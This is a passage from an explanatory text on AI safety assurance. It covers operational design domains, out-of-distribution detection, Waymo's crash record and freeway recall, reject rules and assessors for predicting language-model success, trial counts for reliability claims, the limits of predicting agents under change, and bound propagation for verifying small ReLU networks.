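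In *Defining Operational Conditions for Safety-Critical AI-Based Systems from Data*, Christensen, Köster and colleagues (2026) call the ranges the *taxonomy* of an ODD and the connections between them its *ontology*. They consider some connections almost impossible to write down in advance, such as those that depend on the weather.

Engineers can instead try to learn the boundary from simulations. Bouchekir and Guzman Cancimance gave records of simulated parking to a decision tree, a program that finds if-then rules in data. Somebody has to check the resulting rules, because two of the published ones conflict. For the same light, fog and sun, one rule excludes speeds above about 44 km/h, while the other allows speeds above about 57 km/h if the rain stays below a limit. At 60 km/h in light rain, the car would therefore be both outside and inside its domain.

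### Noticing unfamiliar conditions

The taxi can measure rain with a sensor and look up its position on a map, but some unfamiliar inputs don't break any limit on the list. *Out-of-Distribution Detection for Safety Assurance of AI and Autonomous Systems* (Hodge, Paterson and Habli, 2025) gives the example of traffic signs. A Chinese sign is outside the ODD of a car built for Europe. A rare European sign is inside it, but the network may have seen too few pictures of that sign in training. The network may also have failed to learn another European sign despite seeing plenty of pictures of it. A monitor that checks only place and weather would not flag either European sign.

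*Out-of-distribution detection* is meant to identify inputs that differ from the data used to develop a system. In covariate shift, a common case, the inputs change but the correct answers to them don't. For example, developers may train a vision network on pictures taken by day and then use it at night, when pedestrians look different but should still be labeled as pedestrians. Comparing new inputs with the training data may reveal this change, and may also flag a traffic sign that was rare in training, but it won't flag a common sign that the network never learned.

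Christensen and colleagues use recorded conditions both to define a domain and to detect departures from it. Each recorded condition $x_i$ is a list of $n$ numbers, such as an aircraft's altitude and speed. They put a bell-shaped curve around each of the $N$ recorded conditions and combine the curves into one score for any new condition $x$:

$$\alpha_i(x) = \exp\Big(-\tfrac{1}{2}\sum_{k=1}^{n}\frac{(x_k - x_{ik})^2}{w_{ik}^2}\Big), \qquad \alpha(x) = 1 - \prod_{i=1}^{N}\big(1-\alpha_i(x)\big)$$

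Here $w_{ik}$ is the width of the curve, which is larger where the recorded conditions lie close together. If $x$ is one width away from two recorded conditions and far from all the others, each of the two contributes 0.61, and the score is $1 - 0.39^2 \approx 0.85$. The new condition counts as inside the domain if its score reaches a threshold $\zeta$.

To choose the threshold $\zeta$, engineers set aside some of the recorded conditions and pick a value that wrongly excludes no more than a chosen share, such as 10%, of new conditions of the same kind. If they also have examples of conditions that don't belong in the domain, the program narrows the curves that contribute most to those examples' scores until all of those scores are low enough.

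Christensen and colleagues tested the method on data for two parts of a system that will help pilots avoid other aircraft, one for vertical and one for horizontal manoeuvres. In one test they cut a region out of the vertical data and measured how often a detector would wrongly accept points from it. The simplest detector draws the smallest shape without dents that encloses all the remaining data. It accepted 54.7% of the points, because it also encloses any holes in the data. The method's curves accepted 4.2%, and 0.55% after the researchers gave the program examples from the region to exclude.

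Wrong rejections were much more common. With the threshold set for a 10% error rate, the method rejected about 41% of the test conditions in the vertical domain and 54% of those in the horizontal domain. The 10% rate applies to new conditions that resemble the recorded ones, but many test conditions came from parts of the intended domain that the recordings did not cover. A detector's error rate therefore depends on the conditions the system encounters, just as a language model's rate of illegal chess moves depends on the position.

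Even a 10% false alarm rate would be too high for many uses. A taxi that checked its conditions once a minute would average six false alarms an hour. A lower threshold would cause fewer false alarms but accept more unfamiliar conditions.

Familiar conditions also aren't necessarily safe. If a taxi had often driven too fast past a school while engineers were recording, this method would treat speeding there as part of the taxi's domain. Christensen and colleagues acknowledge this and want the safety of a domain established separately. They also left out detectors that are themselves neural networks, because such a detector would need its own training, evidence and ODD, which raises on a small scale the problem of who verifies the verifier.

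### Leaving the domain

If the monitor raises an alarm, the system switches to a fallback, a simple behaviour that the designers trust. The self-parking car must never hit a pedestrian "unless its velocity is zero", so it can always meet its requirement by stopping. Stopping is reasonable in a car park, but on a freeway a stationary car is a hazard, and the taxi may first have to drive to an exit in conditions it wasn't built for. A designer therefore has to leave a margin between the point where the alarm goes off and the point where the car can no longer drive safely.

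A fallback can also be wrong for the situation. Teoh, Kidd and Riexinger (2026), in *Rise of the machines*, recall how a driverless Cruise car dragged a pedestrian as it pulled over, after another vehicle had thrown the pedestrian into its path. Pulling over is a sensible response to most collisions, but not when someone is under the car.

A stop that is safe for one taxi may not be safe for a whole fleet, and testing one car at a time would not reveal the danger. Suppose a power cut turns off the traffic lights across a city, and every taxi stops at the next junction to wait for instructions from a remote operator. The operators would receive far more calls than usual, and the stationary taxis could block ambulances.

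### Waymo's record on city streets

The best evidence on driverless cars within an ODD comes from Waymo, Alphabet's self-driving company, because other operators publish few or no figures for the miles they drive. *Comparison of Waymo Rider-Only crash rates by crash type to human benchmarks* (2025), a peer-reviewed paper by Waymo's researchers, covers 56.7 million miles without a human driver and uses police records to compare the cars with human drivers. The largest reduction was in collisions between vehicles at intersections, according to *Where ADS Crashes Differ* (2026). eWeek's *Waymo's Safety Stats Are So Good* puts that reduction at 96%, and the reduction in suspected serious injuries at 85%.

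Teoh and his co-authors made an independent comparison for the Insurance Institute for Highway Safety (IIHS), an American research body, and have submitted the preprint to a journal. They compared about 50 million driverless miles from 2021 to 2024 in Phoenix, San Francisco, Los Angeles and Austin with human driving in the same areas and years. Freeways were outside Waymo's ODD during this period, so they excluded freeway driving from the human figures too.

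Waymo had to report even a light scrape to the federal regulator, whereas people often don't tell the police about minor crashes, or even about some that cause injuries. The three researchers therefore read the descriptions of the driverless cars' crashes and judged whether a reasonable person would have reported each one. That left 64 Waymo crashes, or 1.28 per million miles, compared with 4.06 for human drivers. Waymo's rate was 68% lower (95% confidence interval 60% to 75%), and its rate of crashes with injuries was 81% lower.

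Insurance claims offer a check that doesn't depend on police reports. *Credibility-Weighted Pricing of Autonomous Vehicle Liability Under Operational Design Domain Shift* (2026) reports that over 25.3 million miles in the same four cities, Waymo's cars had 88% fewer property damage claims and 92% fewer bodily injury claims than the overall driving population. It also reports nearly as large a reduction compared with recent cars that have modern driver-assistance features.

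The most recent figures come from Waymo itself, which reports 271.3 million driverless miles up to June 2026, now including Atlanta. It reports 82% fewer injury crashes and 95% fewer crashes with serious injuries or deaths than its human benchmark.

The size of the advantage depends heavily on that benchmark. For San Francisco, Waymo puts the human rate at 6.71 injury crashes per million miles, while Teoh and colleagues put it at 1.27. Waymo gives more weight to the parts of the city where its cars drive most, and raises the human figure to account for unreported injuries. Teoh and colleagues use police reports from the whole urban area without adjustment. They still find an injury rate 76% below the human one in San Francisco, compared with 90% by Waymo's calculation. It seems safe to conclude that Waymo's cars crash much less often than human drivers on these streets, but not to give a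 single figure for the difference.

Some of the advantage may come from the domain rather than better driving. Nearly half of Waymo's crashes in the IIHS study happened on roads with speed limits of 25 mph or less, compared with 8% of the human crashes, although the speed limit was unknown for another 24% of the human crashes. Without mileage figures by speed limit, Teoh and colleagues couldn't compare Waymo's crash rates with human drivers' separately for slow and fast roads. Nearly half of the Waymo cars that crashed were empty, which leaves fewer people to injure. The human average also includes drunk and distracted drivers, so a car can beat it without driving as well as a careful person.

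The study found no fatal crashes involving Waymo's driverless cars, but this is weak evidence. At the human rate, about 1.1 fatal crash involvements would be expected over the same distance. The chance of seeing none at that rate is

$$e^{-1.1} \approx 0.33,$$

so an average human driver would have had a one-in-three chance of matching the record. Low failure rates take an enormous amount of driving to establish, as the next section explains.

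In IIHS's *Waymo's driverless cars crash less often than people* (2026), IIHS president David Harkey said that Waymo's cars are safer than human drivers "on a limited scale". Teoh and colleagues also warn that the results may not apply to new locations or other companies. The results don't show how Waymo's cars behave on freeways, which Waymo has since added to its domain.

### Roadworks on the freeway

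In April 2026, six Waymo cars in Phoenix drove past signs closing the ramps to a freeway and entered construction zones. Waymo described what followed in *Part 573 Safety Recall Report 26E035* (2026), filed with the National Highway Traffic Safety Administration, the US road-safety regulator. The company restricted freeway driving, introduced measures to help the cars respond to closures, and then lifted the restrictions. On 18 May, seven cars in the San Francisco Bay Area drove between cones into freeway lanes with active roadworks. Waymo restricted freeway driving again the next day, and in June decided on a recall. Insurance Journal's *Waymo Recalls Thousands of Robotaxis Over Risk of Entering Construction Zones* (2026) reported that the recall covered 3,871 vehicles and was the company's second in just over a month.

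An ODD that lists only "freeways" is evidently too coarse, because driving on a freeway with roadworks is different from driving on the same freeway without them. But a more detailed ODD wouldn't have been enough. According to Waymo, the software in each case may have failed to recognise the construction zone, given too much priority to avoiding other hazards on the freeway, or both. If the fallback depends on the same software recognising the roadworks, it won't start when the software misses them. If the car recognises the zone but swerves into it to avoid something else, the problem is how it weighs one danger against another, which no boundary monitor would correct.

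The incidents also show that failures in a fleet aren't independent. Seven cars with the same software can easily make the same mistake on the same freeways in one day, which would be strange for seven human drivers. An average crash rate over millions of ordinary miles gives little warning of such shared failures.

Making the domain smaller worked because a car that stays off the freeway can't drive into freeway roadworks. Waymo could impose this restriction before it understood the cause. It resumed freeway driving on 25 June, after updating the software. The cars now slow down when they detect that they may be in a construction zone, so they act cautiously even when the detection is uncertain. Waymo also added ways to identify planned roadworks before a car reaches them, so that its cars rely less on detecting the cones.

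Staying within the domain doesn't prevent every accident. School zones are an ordinary part of a taxi's domain, and Teoh and colleagues mention a federal investigation into a Waymo car that struck a nine-year-old child in one, causing minor injuries.

### Approval for a stated use

Waymo could add and remove freeways on its own, but in some industries a regulator has to approve the use first. In US aviation, Part 21 of the federal regulations governs the approval of a specific aircraft design against specific requirements. Khlaaf (2023), in *Toward Comprehensive Risk Assessments and Assurance of AI-Based Systems*, points out that there is no standard way to assess a "generic" vehicle for every purpose. Christensen and colleagues note that the European Union Aviation Safety Agency applies the ODD concept to any AI-based system in aviation.

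Regulators of medical devices also restrict the conditions in which a system operates. In 2018 the US Food and Drug Administration authorised IDx-DR, a program that examines photographs of the retina, to detect damage caused by diabetes. The authorisation covers adults with diabetes who haven't already been diagnosed with that damage. It doesn't cover looking for other eye diseases, even in the same photographs. This narrow use makes the evidence manageable, because the developer can test the program on the kind of patient clinics will use it for. But the authorisation can't stop a clinic from photographing the wrong patient, so someone at the clinic still has to check that each patient is eligible.

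### Models whose tasks are open-ended

A general-purpose language model has no such narrow use. Khlaaf thinks assessments of these models have been unsatisfactory because, without a stated domain, there are too many applications, and therefore too many risks, for anyone to assess. She proposes an operational design domain (ODD) for AI systems in general, which records the application, the people involved, the parts of the system that could lead to harm, the groups it could affect, and the assets at stake. A developer who wants to offer one model for both law and medicine would need a separate risk assessment for each use. She thinks it would be unproductive to insist on evaluating a model for every conceivable task first, just as it would be to wait for a way to certify all vehicles before certifying one aircraft.

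This is good advice for a hospital that wants a model only to summarise discharge letters, because the hospital can collect typical letters, test the model on them and refuse other uses. It is less helpful to a company that offers a chatbot to everyone. Hodge and colleagues observe that the ODD of a car able to drive anywhere would be the whole world. A chatbot that accepts any text has much the same problem, because an ODD that excludes nothing does not make any claim about the system easier to establish.

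A developer could try to exclude some topics, but there is no agreed list of conditions for free text. A sensor can measure rain in standard units, but nothing similar exists for "legal advice". People could reasonably disagree about whether a question about a neighbour's fence is a legal one, and a conversation can move from recipes to drug doses. An assessor can use Khlaaf's categories to decide what to consider, but they don't include a test that a program could run on each message.

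One could convert each message into a list of numbers, as language models do internally, and apply a detector such as Christensen and colleagues' curves. But the method treats nearby points as alike. Changing "5 mg" to "5 g" in a question about medicine barely changes the wording but makes the dose a thousand times larger. Such a detector might still be useful for noticing text in an unfamiliar language or format, but it couldn't reliably tell safe requests from dangerous ones.

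It is often better to give up free text. A pharmacy could have its staff select a drug from a list and enter the patient's age and weight in boxes, and a short program could then write the question for the model. The program can check that each input is within its allowed range, as in the taxi's ODD. The staff can no longer ask about anything else, and the pharmacy still has to test the model's answers within those ranges. If the model can also take actions, the designer can limit those too, with shields that check each action or permissions that restrict what a software agent may read and do. Later sections cover both methods.

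Developers can also limit a model's ODD to certain users, much as a self-driving car's ODD limits it to certain roads. A user's identity is easier to check than the meaning of a message. This matters most for functions that are useful to both defenders and attackers. A request to find the security flaws in a program may come from the company that wrote it or from a criminal. If both use the same words, no rule about the text can separate them, but a developer can verify the company's identity and give only approved organisations access to the model's full hacking abilities.

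Restricted release depends on approved users having honest purposes, keeping their accounts secure and not sharing their access. Even if they do all this, the restriction makes misuse less likely but does not make the model more reliable. An honest security team may still get a wrong answer, or find that an agent has attacked the wrong computer. If someone steals or publishes the model itself, the developer can no longer control who uses it.

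## Estimating from tests where a system can be relied on

A developer who has limited an AI system to certain users, places or tasks still doesn't know which of the remaining cases it will get right. Tests usually produce an average, such as 90% correct, which is little help in deciding whether to trust the system with a particular case.

### Six cars with the same success rate

Zhou, Casares and colleagues, in *Predictable artificial intelligence* (2026), imagine six self-driving cars, A to F, that each succeed on 62.5% of their journeys. Car A's failures depend on how winding the road is, car B's on how thick the fog is, and those of cars C and D on both. The failures of cars E and F follow no simple rule based on bends or fog. The owner of car A can look at a map and use the car only when the road is straight enough, while the owner of car F takes much the same risk on every trip. Zhou,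 Casares and colleagues would therefore prefer car A. They think full verification is no longer feasible for many AI systems and an average success rate is no longer enough, so developers should aim to predict where a system will succeed.

Their *validity envelope* makes this precise. Let $e$ be one use of the system, such as one journey, and let $v$ be 1 if the system succeeds and 0 if it fails. Before each use, a predictor gives a probability of success $\hat p(e)$. The envelope is the largest set of uses for which

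$$\mathbb{E}\big[\hat p(e)\big] \ge \omega \quad\text{and}\quad \mathbb{E}\big[(\hat p(e) - v)^2\big] \le \sigma,$$

where $\mathbb{E}$ is the average over the set. The threshold $\omega$ is the lowest acceptable rate of predicted success, and $\sigma$ is the highest acceptable prediction error. The definition allows other measures of error, but this one, the *Brier score*, is common. A forecast of 90% costs 0.01 if the system succeeds and 0.81 if it fails.

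Both thresholds are necessary. If a predictor gave every journey a 99% chance of success for a car that fails on half its journeys, the journeys would pass $\omega = 0.95$, but the prediction error would be 0.49. A low prediction error isn't enough either, because a car that crashed on every journey would be perfectly predictable.

Suppose $\omega = 0.95$ and $\sigma = 0.05$. The best forecast for car F is a 62.5% chance of success on every journey, so its envelope is empty. In the simplest case, car A always succeeds on the straighter roads and always fails on the rest, and its envelope contains all the journeys on straighter roads. But because the thresholds apply to averages, the largest set that meets them can also include some winding journeys that are correctly predicted to fail, up to 5% of the set. A designer would want to exclude those, which requires judging each journey separately.

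An envelope also depends on the predictor. An earlier version of the paper, *Predictable Artificial Intelligence* (2023), noted that some things look unpredictable until a new method or more effort reveals a pattern. If car F turned out to fail only when the sun is low, its owner could use it as safely as car A.

### Refusing the cases that will probably fail

A *reject rule* accepts a case only if $\hat p(e) \ge \tau$, where the developer chooses the threshold $\tau$. The forecast $\hat p(e)$ can come from an *assessor*, a separate model that predicts whether the system will succeed. To build one, developers run the system on many test cases, record which ones it gets right, and train the assessor to predict the result from features of the case. They then try different values of $\tau$ on held-out test cases until the accepted cases meet both $\omega$ and $\sigma$. In use, the assessor runs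 first and the system receives only the cases that the rule accepts, so the rule sets the boundary of the deployment. A person or a more reliable system can handle the rejected cases.

An assessor is *calibrated* if its forecasts match what happens, so that the system succeeds on 80% of the cases rated at 80%. With a calibrated assessor, the system's average success rate on accepted cases is at least $\tau$.

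Zhou, Casares and colleagues describe an experiment in which four versions of GPT-3, an early large language model, converted messy data into a standard format. The researchers set the threshold $\tau$ at only 1%, so they refused only the requests that looked hopeless. This avoided 46% of the failures and lost 1.5% of the correct answers. Without the rule, GPT-3 would have got 552 of every 1,000 requests right and 448 wrong. With it, GPT-3 got about 544 right and 242 wrong, which raised the success rate on accepted requests from 55.2% to 69.2%. That saves money, but nearly a third of the accepted answers were still wrong. A higher threshold would remove more of them but also refuse more requests that GPT-3 could have handled.

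A system can also estimate its own chance of success. GPT-3's confidence predicted whether its answers were correct slightly better than the assessor did, with the largest version scoring a Brier score of 0.096 against the assessor's 0.125. But the model has to run before anyone can read its confidence, which is too late to save the money spent running it or to prevent an action an agent has already taken. Training on human preferences has also made some later models' confidence less accurate.

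People are not very good at estimating where an AI system can be relied on. In experiments by Dreyfuss and Raux, which the paper summarises, participants lost trust in an AI after one mistake on a question they found easy, and trusted it too much after one success on a hard question. Their forecasts had an average Brier score of about 0.25, the score someone would get by answering "50%" every time.

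### How well assessors predict language models

The share of correct forecasts is a misleading way to grade an assessor. One example in the paper is a program that sends each customer complaint to one of five departments at random, and so is right 20% of the time. The paper defines predictability as the chance that the best predictor correctly anticipates success or failure, and puts the program's predictability at 20% too. That seems to be a mistake, since a predictor that always forecast failure would be right 80% of the time. That predictor would score well but be useless for a reject rule, because it would reject everything.

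Researchers therefore often measure *discrimination*, which is how well the forecasts separate successes from failures. Take every pair of one success $i$ and one failure $j$, and count how often the success had the higher forecast $c$:

$$\text{AUROC} = \frac{1}{n_{\text{succ}}\, n_{\text{fail}}}\sum_{i\,:\,v_i=1}\ \sum_{j\,:\,v_j=0} \mathbf{1}[c_i > c_j]$$

The name stands for "area under the receiver operating characteristic curve". A perfect assessor scores 1, and one that guesses scores about 0.5.

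In *PredictaBoard*, Pacchiardi, Voudouris and colleagues (2025) tested assessors on 41 language models, including three versions of GPT-4o, using the models' results on MMLU-Pro, a set of 11,383 exam questions. They trained 12 assessors for each model, 492 in total, by combining four ways of turning a question's text into numbers with three standard prediction methods. The assessors could use the question but not the model's answer. Most assessors did about as well as chance, and the best had an AUROC of around 0.7.

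They also measured how many questions each pair could accept while keeping errors below a chosen limit. The best pairs did well when up to 20% of accepted answers could be wrong, but that limit isn't very demanding for a model that already gets 75% right. With a limit of 10%, the share of accepted questions fell sharply, and with limits below 5% it was close to zero for every assessor. Results were even worse on BIG-Bench Hard, a collection of difficult reasoning tasks that the researchers had left out of the assessors' training. The pairs that did best on familiar questions weren't the best on these tasks, so a developer can't assume that the best pair on one test will also be the best elsewhere.

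In *General Scales Unlock AI Evaluation with Explanatory and Predictive Power*, Zhou, Pacchiardi and colleagues (2025) trained assessors on ratings of what each question requires. They wrote 18 scales, from 0 to "5 or above", for demands such as logical reasoning, knowledge of social science, and understanding what other people think. A puzzle about where Sally will look for a marble that Anne has moved might rate 4 for understanding other minds and 0 for mathematics. A language model applied the scales to 16,108 questions from 63 tasks in 20 benchmarks, and added a nineteenth rating for how hard it is to guess the answer. They then ran 15 language models on the questions and trained an assessor for each model to predict its success from the 19 ratings.

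These assessors had an average AUROC of 0.84 on familiar tasks. It was 0.81 when whole tasks were kept out of training and 0.75 when whole benchmarks were. An assessor made by training a language model on the text of the questions did equally well on familiar tasks but fell to 0.79 on new ones and much further on new benchmarks. Human-readable demands therefore seem to carry over to new material better than patterns in the wording do. The demand-based assessors also train faster, taking four seconds for each model compared with 300 hours for the text-based assessor, though someone still has to run the model on the questions first.

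The 18 scales do not explain all of the gap between 0.84 and PredictaBoard's 0.7. A simple assessor that used only the words of each question scored 0.80 in the same study, yet similar assessors were mostly near chance in PredictaBoard. This difference probably comes largely from the questions. With 20 benchmarks of very different difficulty, an assessor can do well by recognising the kind of question, while MMLU-Pro's questions are more alike.

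The researchers attribute the drop on new benchmarks mainly to gaps in the data. Twenty benchmarks don't cover every combination of demands, and too few of the questions were very hard for the strongest models. AUROC fell most, by 0.05 to 0.11, for models trained to reason step by step, including OpenAI's o1, from 2024. Even fewer of the questions would be hard for newer models.

The assessors based on demands were also well calibrated, with an average error of about 1 percentage point on familiar tasks and 4 on new benchmarks. An error of 1 point hardly matters when the forecast is 70%, but if the forecast is 99.9% and the true rate is 98.9%, the system will fail eleven times as often as expected. A low average calibration error therefore doesn't show that a reject rule is safe at very high thresholds.

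### Predicting what agents will do

An agent is harder to assess because it carries out many steps and can cause damage along the way. *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (2026) proposes separate scores for consistency, robustness, predictability and safety. The consistency score is calculated by running the agent several times on each task, finding the share $q$ of runs that succeed, and averaging $(2q-1)^2$ over all the tasks. An agent scores 0.64 on a task if it succeeds in nine out of ten runs, and 0 if it succeeds in five. It scores 1 if it fails every time, so the consistency score is useful only alongside the success rate.

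The score for predictability is the AUROC of the agent's confidence. *Reliability Engineering for AI Systems* (2026) rightly also counts calibration as part of predictability. Suppose an agent reports 99% confidence whenever it succeeds and 98% whenever it fails. Its AUROC is a perfect 1, but a rule that rejects anything below 95% confidence would accept every failure.

Safety is harder to reduce to a number. *Reliability Engineering for AI Systems* warns that most of an agent's failures are harmless but a few are catastrophic. *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* gives a minor violation a weight of 0.25, a medium one 0.5 and a severe one 1. Deleting a company's only copy of its records would therefore count as much as four minor violations, though most companies would accept more than four to avoid it. It seems better to set a separate limit for the worst failures than to average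 them with the rest.

The time a human expert would need for a task predicts agents' average success well. Zhou, Casares and colleagues describe work on software and cybersecurity tasks in which the chance of success fell along a smooth curve as this time increased. They attribute the decline to the number of steps at which an agent can fail. If each step succeeds 99% of the time and failures are independent, a 100-step task succeeds with probability $0.99^{100} \approx 0.37$. Expert time is useful for estimating how many of next month's tasks an agent will complete, but it gives two equally long tasks the same forecast even if the agent will succeed at one and fail at the other. Pacchiardi and colleagues cite a case in which people couldn't reliably anticipate a coding agent's failures.

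### How many trials without a failure are enough

Whatever the assessor predicts, developers can check the accepted cases directly by running the system on a fresh sample of them. If a failure would be serious, they hope to see none at all. Suppose that each trial fails with probability $p$, independently of the others. The chance of $n$ trials without a failure is $(1-p)^n$. To claim with confidence $C$ that the failure rate is below $p$, we need enough trials that a system with failure rate $p$ would have at most a $1-C$ chance of passing them all:

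$$(1-p)^n \le 1-C.$$

Taking logarithms, and using the fact that $\ln(1-p) \approx -p$ when $p$ is small, gives

$$n \approx \frac{\ln\big(1/(1-C)\big)}{p}.$$

For 95% confidence, the numerator is $\ln 20 \approx 3$, so the number of trials needed without a failure is about $3/p$. To support a failure rate below 1 in 1,000, a developer needs about 3,000 such trials. A system with a failure rate of 1 in 1,000 or worse would pass this test at most one time in 20. This doesn't mean a system that passes has a 95% chance of being that reliable, which would also depend on what we knew before the test.

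Nidhi Kalra and Susan Paddock of the RAND Corporation, an American research institute, applied this formula to self-driving cars in *Driving to Safety* (2016). Human drivers in the United States were causing 1.09 deaths per 100 million miles. If we treat each mile as a trial, the distance a car would have to drive without a death is

$$n \approx \frac{3.00}{1.09 \times 10^{-8}} \approx 275 \text{ million miles}.$$

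A fleet of 100 cars driving day and night at 25 miles per hour would need about twelve and a half years to complete the test without a death. If one death occurred, reaching the same confidence would require about 435 million miles. Either result would show only that the cars are no worse than human drivers.

The numbers are more discouraging still for a system that must never fail. Suppose a company wants a 90% chance of getting through $N$ uses without a single failure. The failure rate has to be below about $0.105/N$, which takes

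$$n \approx \frac{3}{0.105/N} \approx 28N$$

trials without a failure. The company would have to test the system about 28 times as much as it plans to use it. For a system that makes ten billion decisions, this is 280 billion trials. Only a simulation could supply so many, and the result would then depend on how closely the simulation matches the real world.

The formula also assumes that the trials are independent. If a tester writes 3,000 prompts by rewording 100 questions, and the model always treats the different wordings alike, the test has only 100 independent trials. The failure rate could then be almost 3%, not 0.1%.

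Another assumption is that the system doesn't change. Waymo's 271 million driverless miles come close to Kalra and Paddock's figure, but the company has updated its software along the way. A strict tester would start counting again after each update. Engineers can often reasonably argue that a small change to the route planner couldn't have made the brakes worse, but that argument is based on how the car works rather than on the formula.

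The conditions have to stay the same too. Suppose a car completes 3,000 test journeys without a failure, 30 of them in fog. Its overall failure rate is probably below 0.1%, but 30 journeys are only enough to show that its failure rate in fog is probably below about 10%. If the company then moves to a city where half of all journeys are foggy, the tests can't rule out an overall failure rate of almost 5%. The company could fix this by testing more in fog. If the new conditions never occur in the tests, even an unlimited number of those tests may not be enough.

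### When an agent meets something new

Bellot, Richens and Everitt (2025), in *The Limits of Predicting Agents from Behaviour*, study this problem for an agent whose goal we know. They assume that the agent has a world model, a mathematical description of how its environment responds to its actions, and always chooses the action with the best expected result according to that model. We can watch the agent in its original environment for as long as we like, but we can't look at its model, and we want to predict what it will do after a specified change to the environment.

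An agent is *grounded* if its model correctly predicts the effects of every available decision in the original environment. Training by trial and error might produce this strong form of competence. An agent is *weakly predictable* after a change if we can identify at least one decision it would not make under any model consistent with our observations. It is *strongly predictable* if we can rule out all decisions but one in this way. Weak predictability is enough for safety when the decision we can rule out is the dangerous one.

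In their example, an AI chooses between two treatments, 0 and 1. Whether a treatment works depends partly on the patient's blood pressure. The AI is grounded, so it correctly predicts how patients will respond. The hospital now wants to use it for patients who also take a second drug, which gives them all healthy blood pressure. Which treatment will the AI choose?

Suppose there are five equally common types of patient, which neither the AI nor an observer can tell apart directly. In the table, 1 means the treatment works and 0 means it doesn't. The columns for the second drug show what the AI would predict under each of two possible models.

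| Patient type | Healthy blood pressure already? | Treatment 0, no second drug | Treatment 1, no second drug | Model 1, second drug: treatment 0 | Model 1, second drug: treatment 1 | Model 2, second drug: treatment 0 | Model 2, second drug: treatment 1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Yes | 0 | 1 | 0 | 1 | 0 | 1 |
| 2 | No | 0 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 0 |
| 3 | No | 1 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| 4 | Yes | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
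| 5 | No | 0 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| **Success rate** | | **40%** | **60%** | **20%** | **80%** | **80%** | **40%** |

Both models make the same predictions when the second drug is absent, so an AI with either model chooses treatment 1, and watching its choices in those conditions can't reveal which model it has. When the second drug is present, an AI with model 1 still chooses treatment 1, but an AI with model 2 switches to treatment 0. If model 1 describes the patients correctly, that switch cuts the success rate from 80% to 20%, even though the AI would have made no mistake in any earlier test.

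The models can differ only on patient types 2, 3 and 5. Types 1 and 4 already have healthy blood pressure, so the second drug changes nothing for them. Treatment 0 works for one of these two types and treatment 1 works for both. We have never seen the other three types with healthy blood pressure, so either treatment might work for all of them or for none. The AI's predicted success rate could therefore be anywhere from 20% to 80% for treatment 0 and from 40% to 100% for treatment 1. These ranges overlap, so we can't rule out either choice.

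Theorem 1 in the paper turns this reasoning into a general test. We can rule out a decision exactly when some other decision is better even if we assume the worst about the other decision and the best about this one. Let $z$ be the value that the change imposes, here healthy blood pressure. If each outcome is either success ($Y=1$) or failure, and the AI has no further information about the individual patient, we can rule out decision $d^*$ if there is another decision $d$ with

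$$P_d(Y{=}1, z) \;>\; P_{d^*}(Y{=}1, z) + 1 - P_{d^*}(z).$$

The left side includes only the successes of $d$ observed with the value $z$, which amounts to assuming that $d$ fails everywhere else, while the right side is calculated as if $d^*$ succeeds everywhere else. In the example, 0.4 is not greater than 0.8, so we cannot rule out treatment 0.

The test is easier to pass if the new condition was already common. Suppose that 90% of patients had healthy blood pressure, and that treatment 1 worked for 80% of them and treatment 0 for 40%. With the second drug, the AI's estimated success rate across all patients must be at least 72% for treatment 1 and at most 46% for treatment 0, so we can be sure it will choose treatment 1. Developers therefore have a mathematical reason to vary the conditions in their tests, since even many more tests under the usual conditions would not narrow these ranges.

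Real systems will often be harder to predict than this, because the assumptions make the observer's task easier. A real agent may make mistakes, follow habits or choose partly at random, so it might still make a decision that looks clearly worse to it, and a theorem about perfect choices can't by itself rule that out. It may also have a poor model of decisions it has rarely tried. The theorem further assumes that the observer knows what the agent is trying to maximise, which developers can't take for granted with a language model. Bellot and colleagues go on to relax some of their assumptions.

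In another way the theorem is too pessimistic for everyday use. It counts every model that fits the observations as possible, however strange. A doctor might know from biology that model 2 is very unlikely and predict the AI's choice with some confidence, if the AI has learned the same biology. Like Yampolskiy's proof about superintelligence, the theorem limits what we can know for certain, but we can still make good guesses.

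Instead of working out the AI's model, the hospital can do something easier and let the AI make recommendations for patients who take the second drug, while doctors continue to choose the treatment themselves. If the AI recommends treatment 0, the hospital learns this before anyone acts on it. But someone first has to realise that the second drug might matter.

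## Proving properties of a neural network over a set of inputs

The observer in Bellot and colleagues' theorem can watch an AI system but can't look inside it. A developer who has the network itself can use a program to calculate limits on its output for a whole set of inputs at once, because a trained network is a fixed formula.

Each neuron in a network multiplies its inputs by fixed weights, adds them up and usually applies a simple function to the total. In most of the networks that researchers verify, that function is the rectified linear unit, or ReLU:

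$$\text{ReLU}(z) = \max(0, z).$$

The ReLU function replaces negative numbers with zero and leaves positive numbers unchanged. Without a nonlinear function like this, a network could compute only weighted sums of its inputs, and proving its properties would be easy.

### Three ways to bound one small network

The following network has one input and two neurons:

$$f(x) = \text{ReLU}(x) - 2\,\text{ReLU}(x - 0.5), \qquad -1 \le x \le 1.$$

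Suppose we want to prove that $f(x) \le 0.6$. We can see this from the graph of $f$, which is 0 for negative $x$, rises to 0.5 at $x = 0.5$ and falls back to 0 at $x = 1$. But we can't graph a network with thousands of inputs, so verifiers need methods that work without a graph.

The method that requires the least computation, *interval bound propagation*, tracks only the range of each neuron. The first neuron's output lies between 0 and 1. The second neuron's input lies between −1.5 and 0.5, so its output lies between 0 and 0.5. The upper bound on $f$ is therefore $1 - 2 \cdot 0 = 1$. As with $x - x$ earlier, this bound is too loose to prove the claim. It combines an output of 1 from the first neuron with an output of 0 from the second, which can't occur together because the first output requires $x = 1$ and the second requires $x \le 0.5$.

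In deep networks, these errors grow from layer to layer. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026), in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*, replaced some of the tighter bounds inside a verifier with intervals. The final bounds changed by up to 5.6 for a four-layer network and by up to 792 for a six-layer network.

A tighter method called CROWN encloses each ReLU between two straight lines, so that the final bound still depends on $x$. If a neuron's input $z$ lies between a negative number $l$ and a positive number $u$, then

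$$\lambda z \;\le\; \text{ReLU}(z) \;\le\; \frac{u}{u-l}\,(z - l)$$

for any slope $\lambda$ between 0 and 1. To bound $f$ from above, we need the upper line for the first neuron and the lower line for the second, because $f$ subtracts the second. The first neuron has $l = -1$ and $u = 1$, which gives

$$f(x) \;\le\; \frac{x+1}{2} - 2\lambda(x - 0.5) \;=\; (0.5 - 2\lambda)\,x + 0.5 + \lambda.$$

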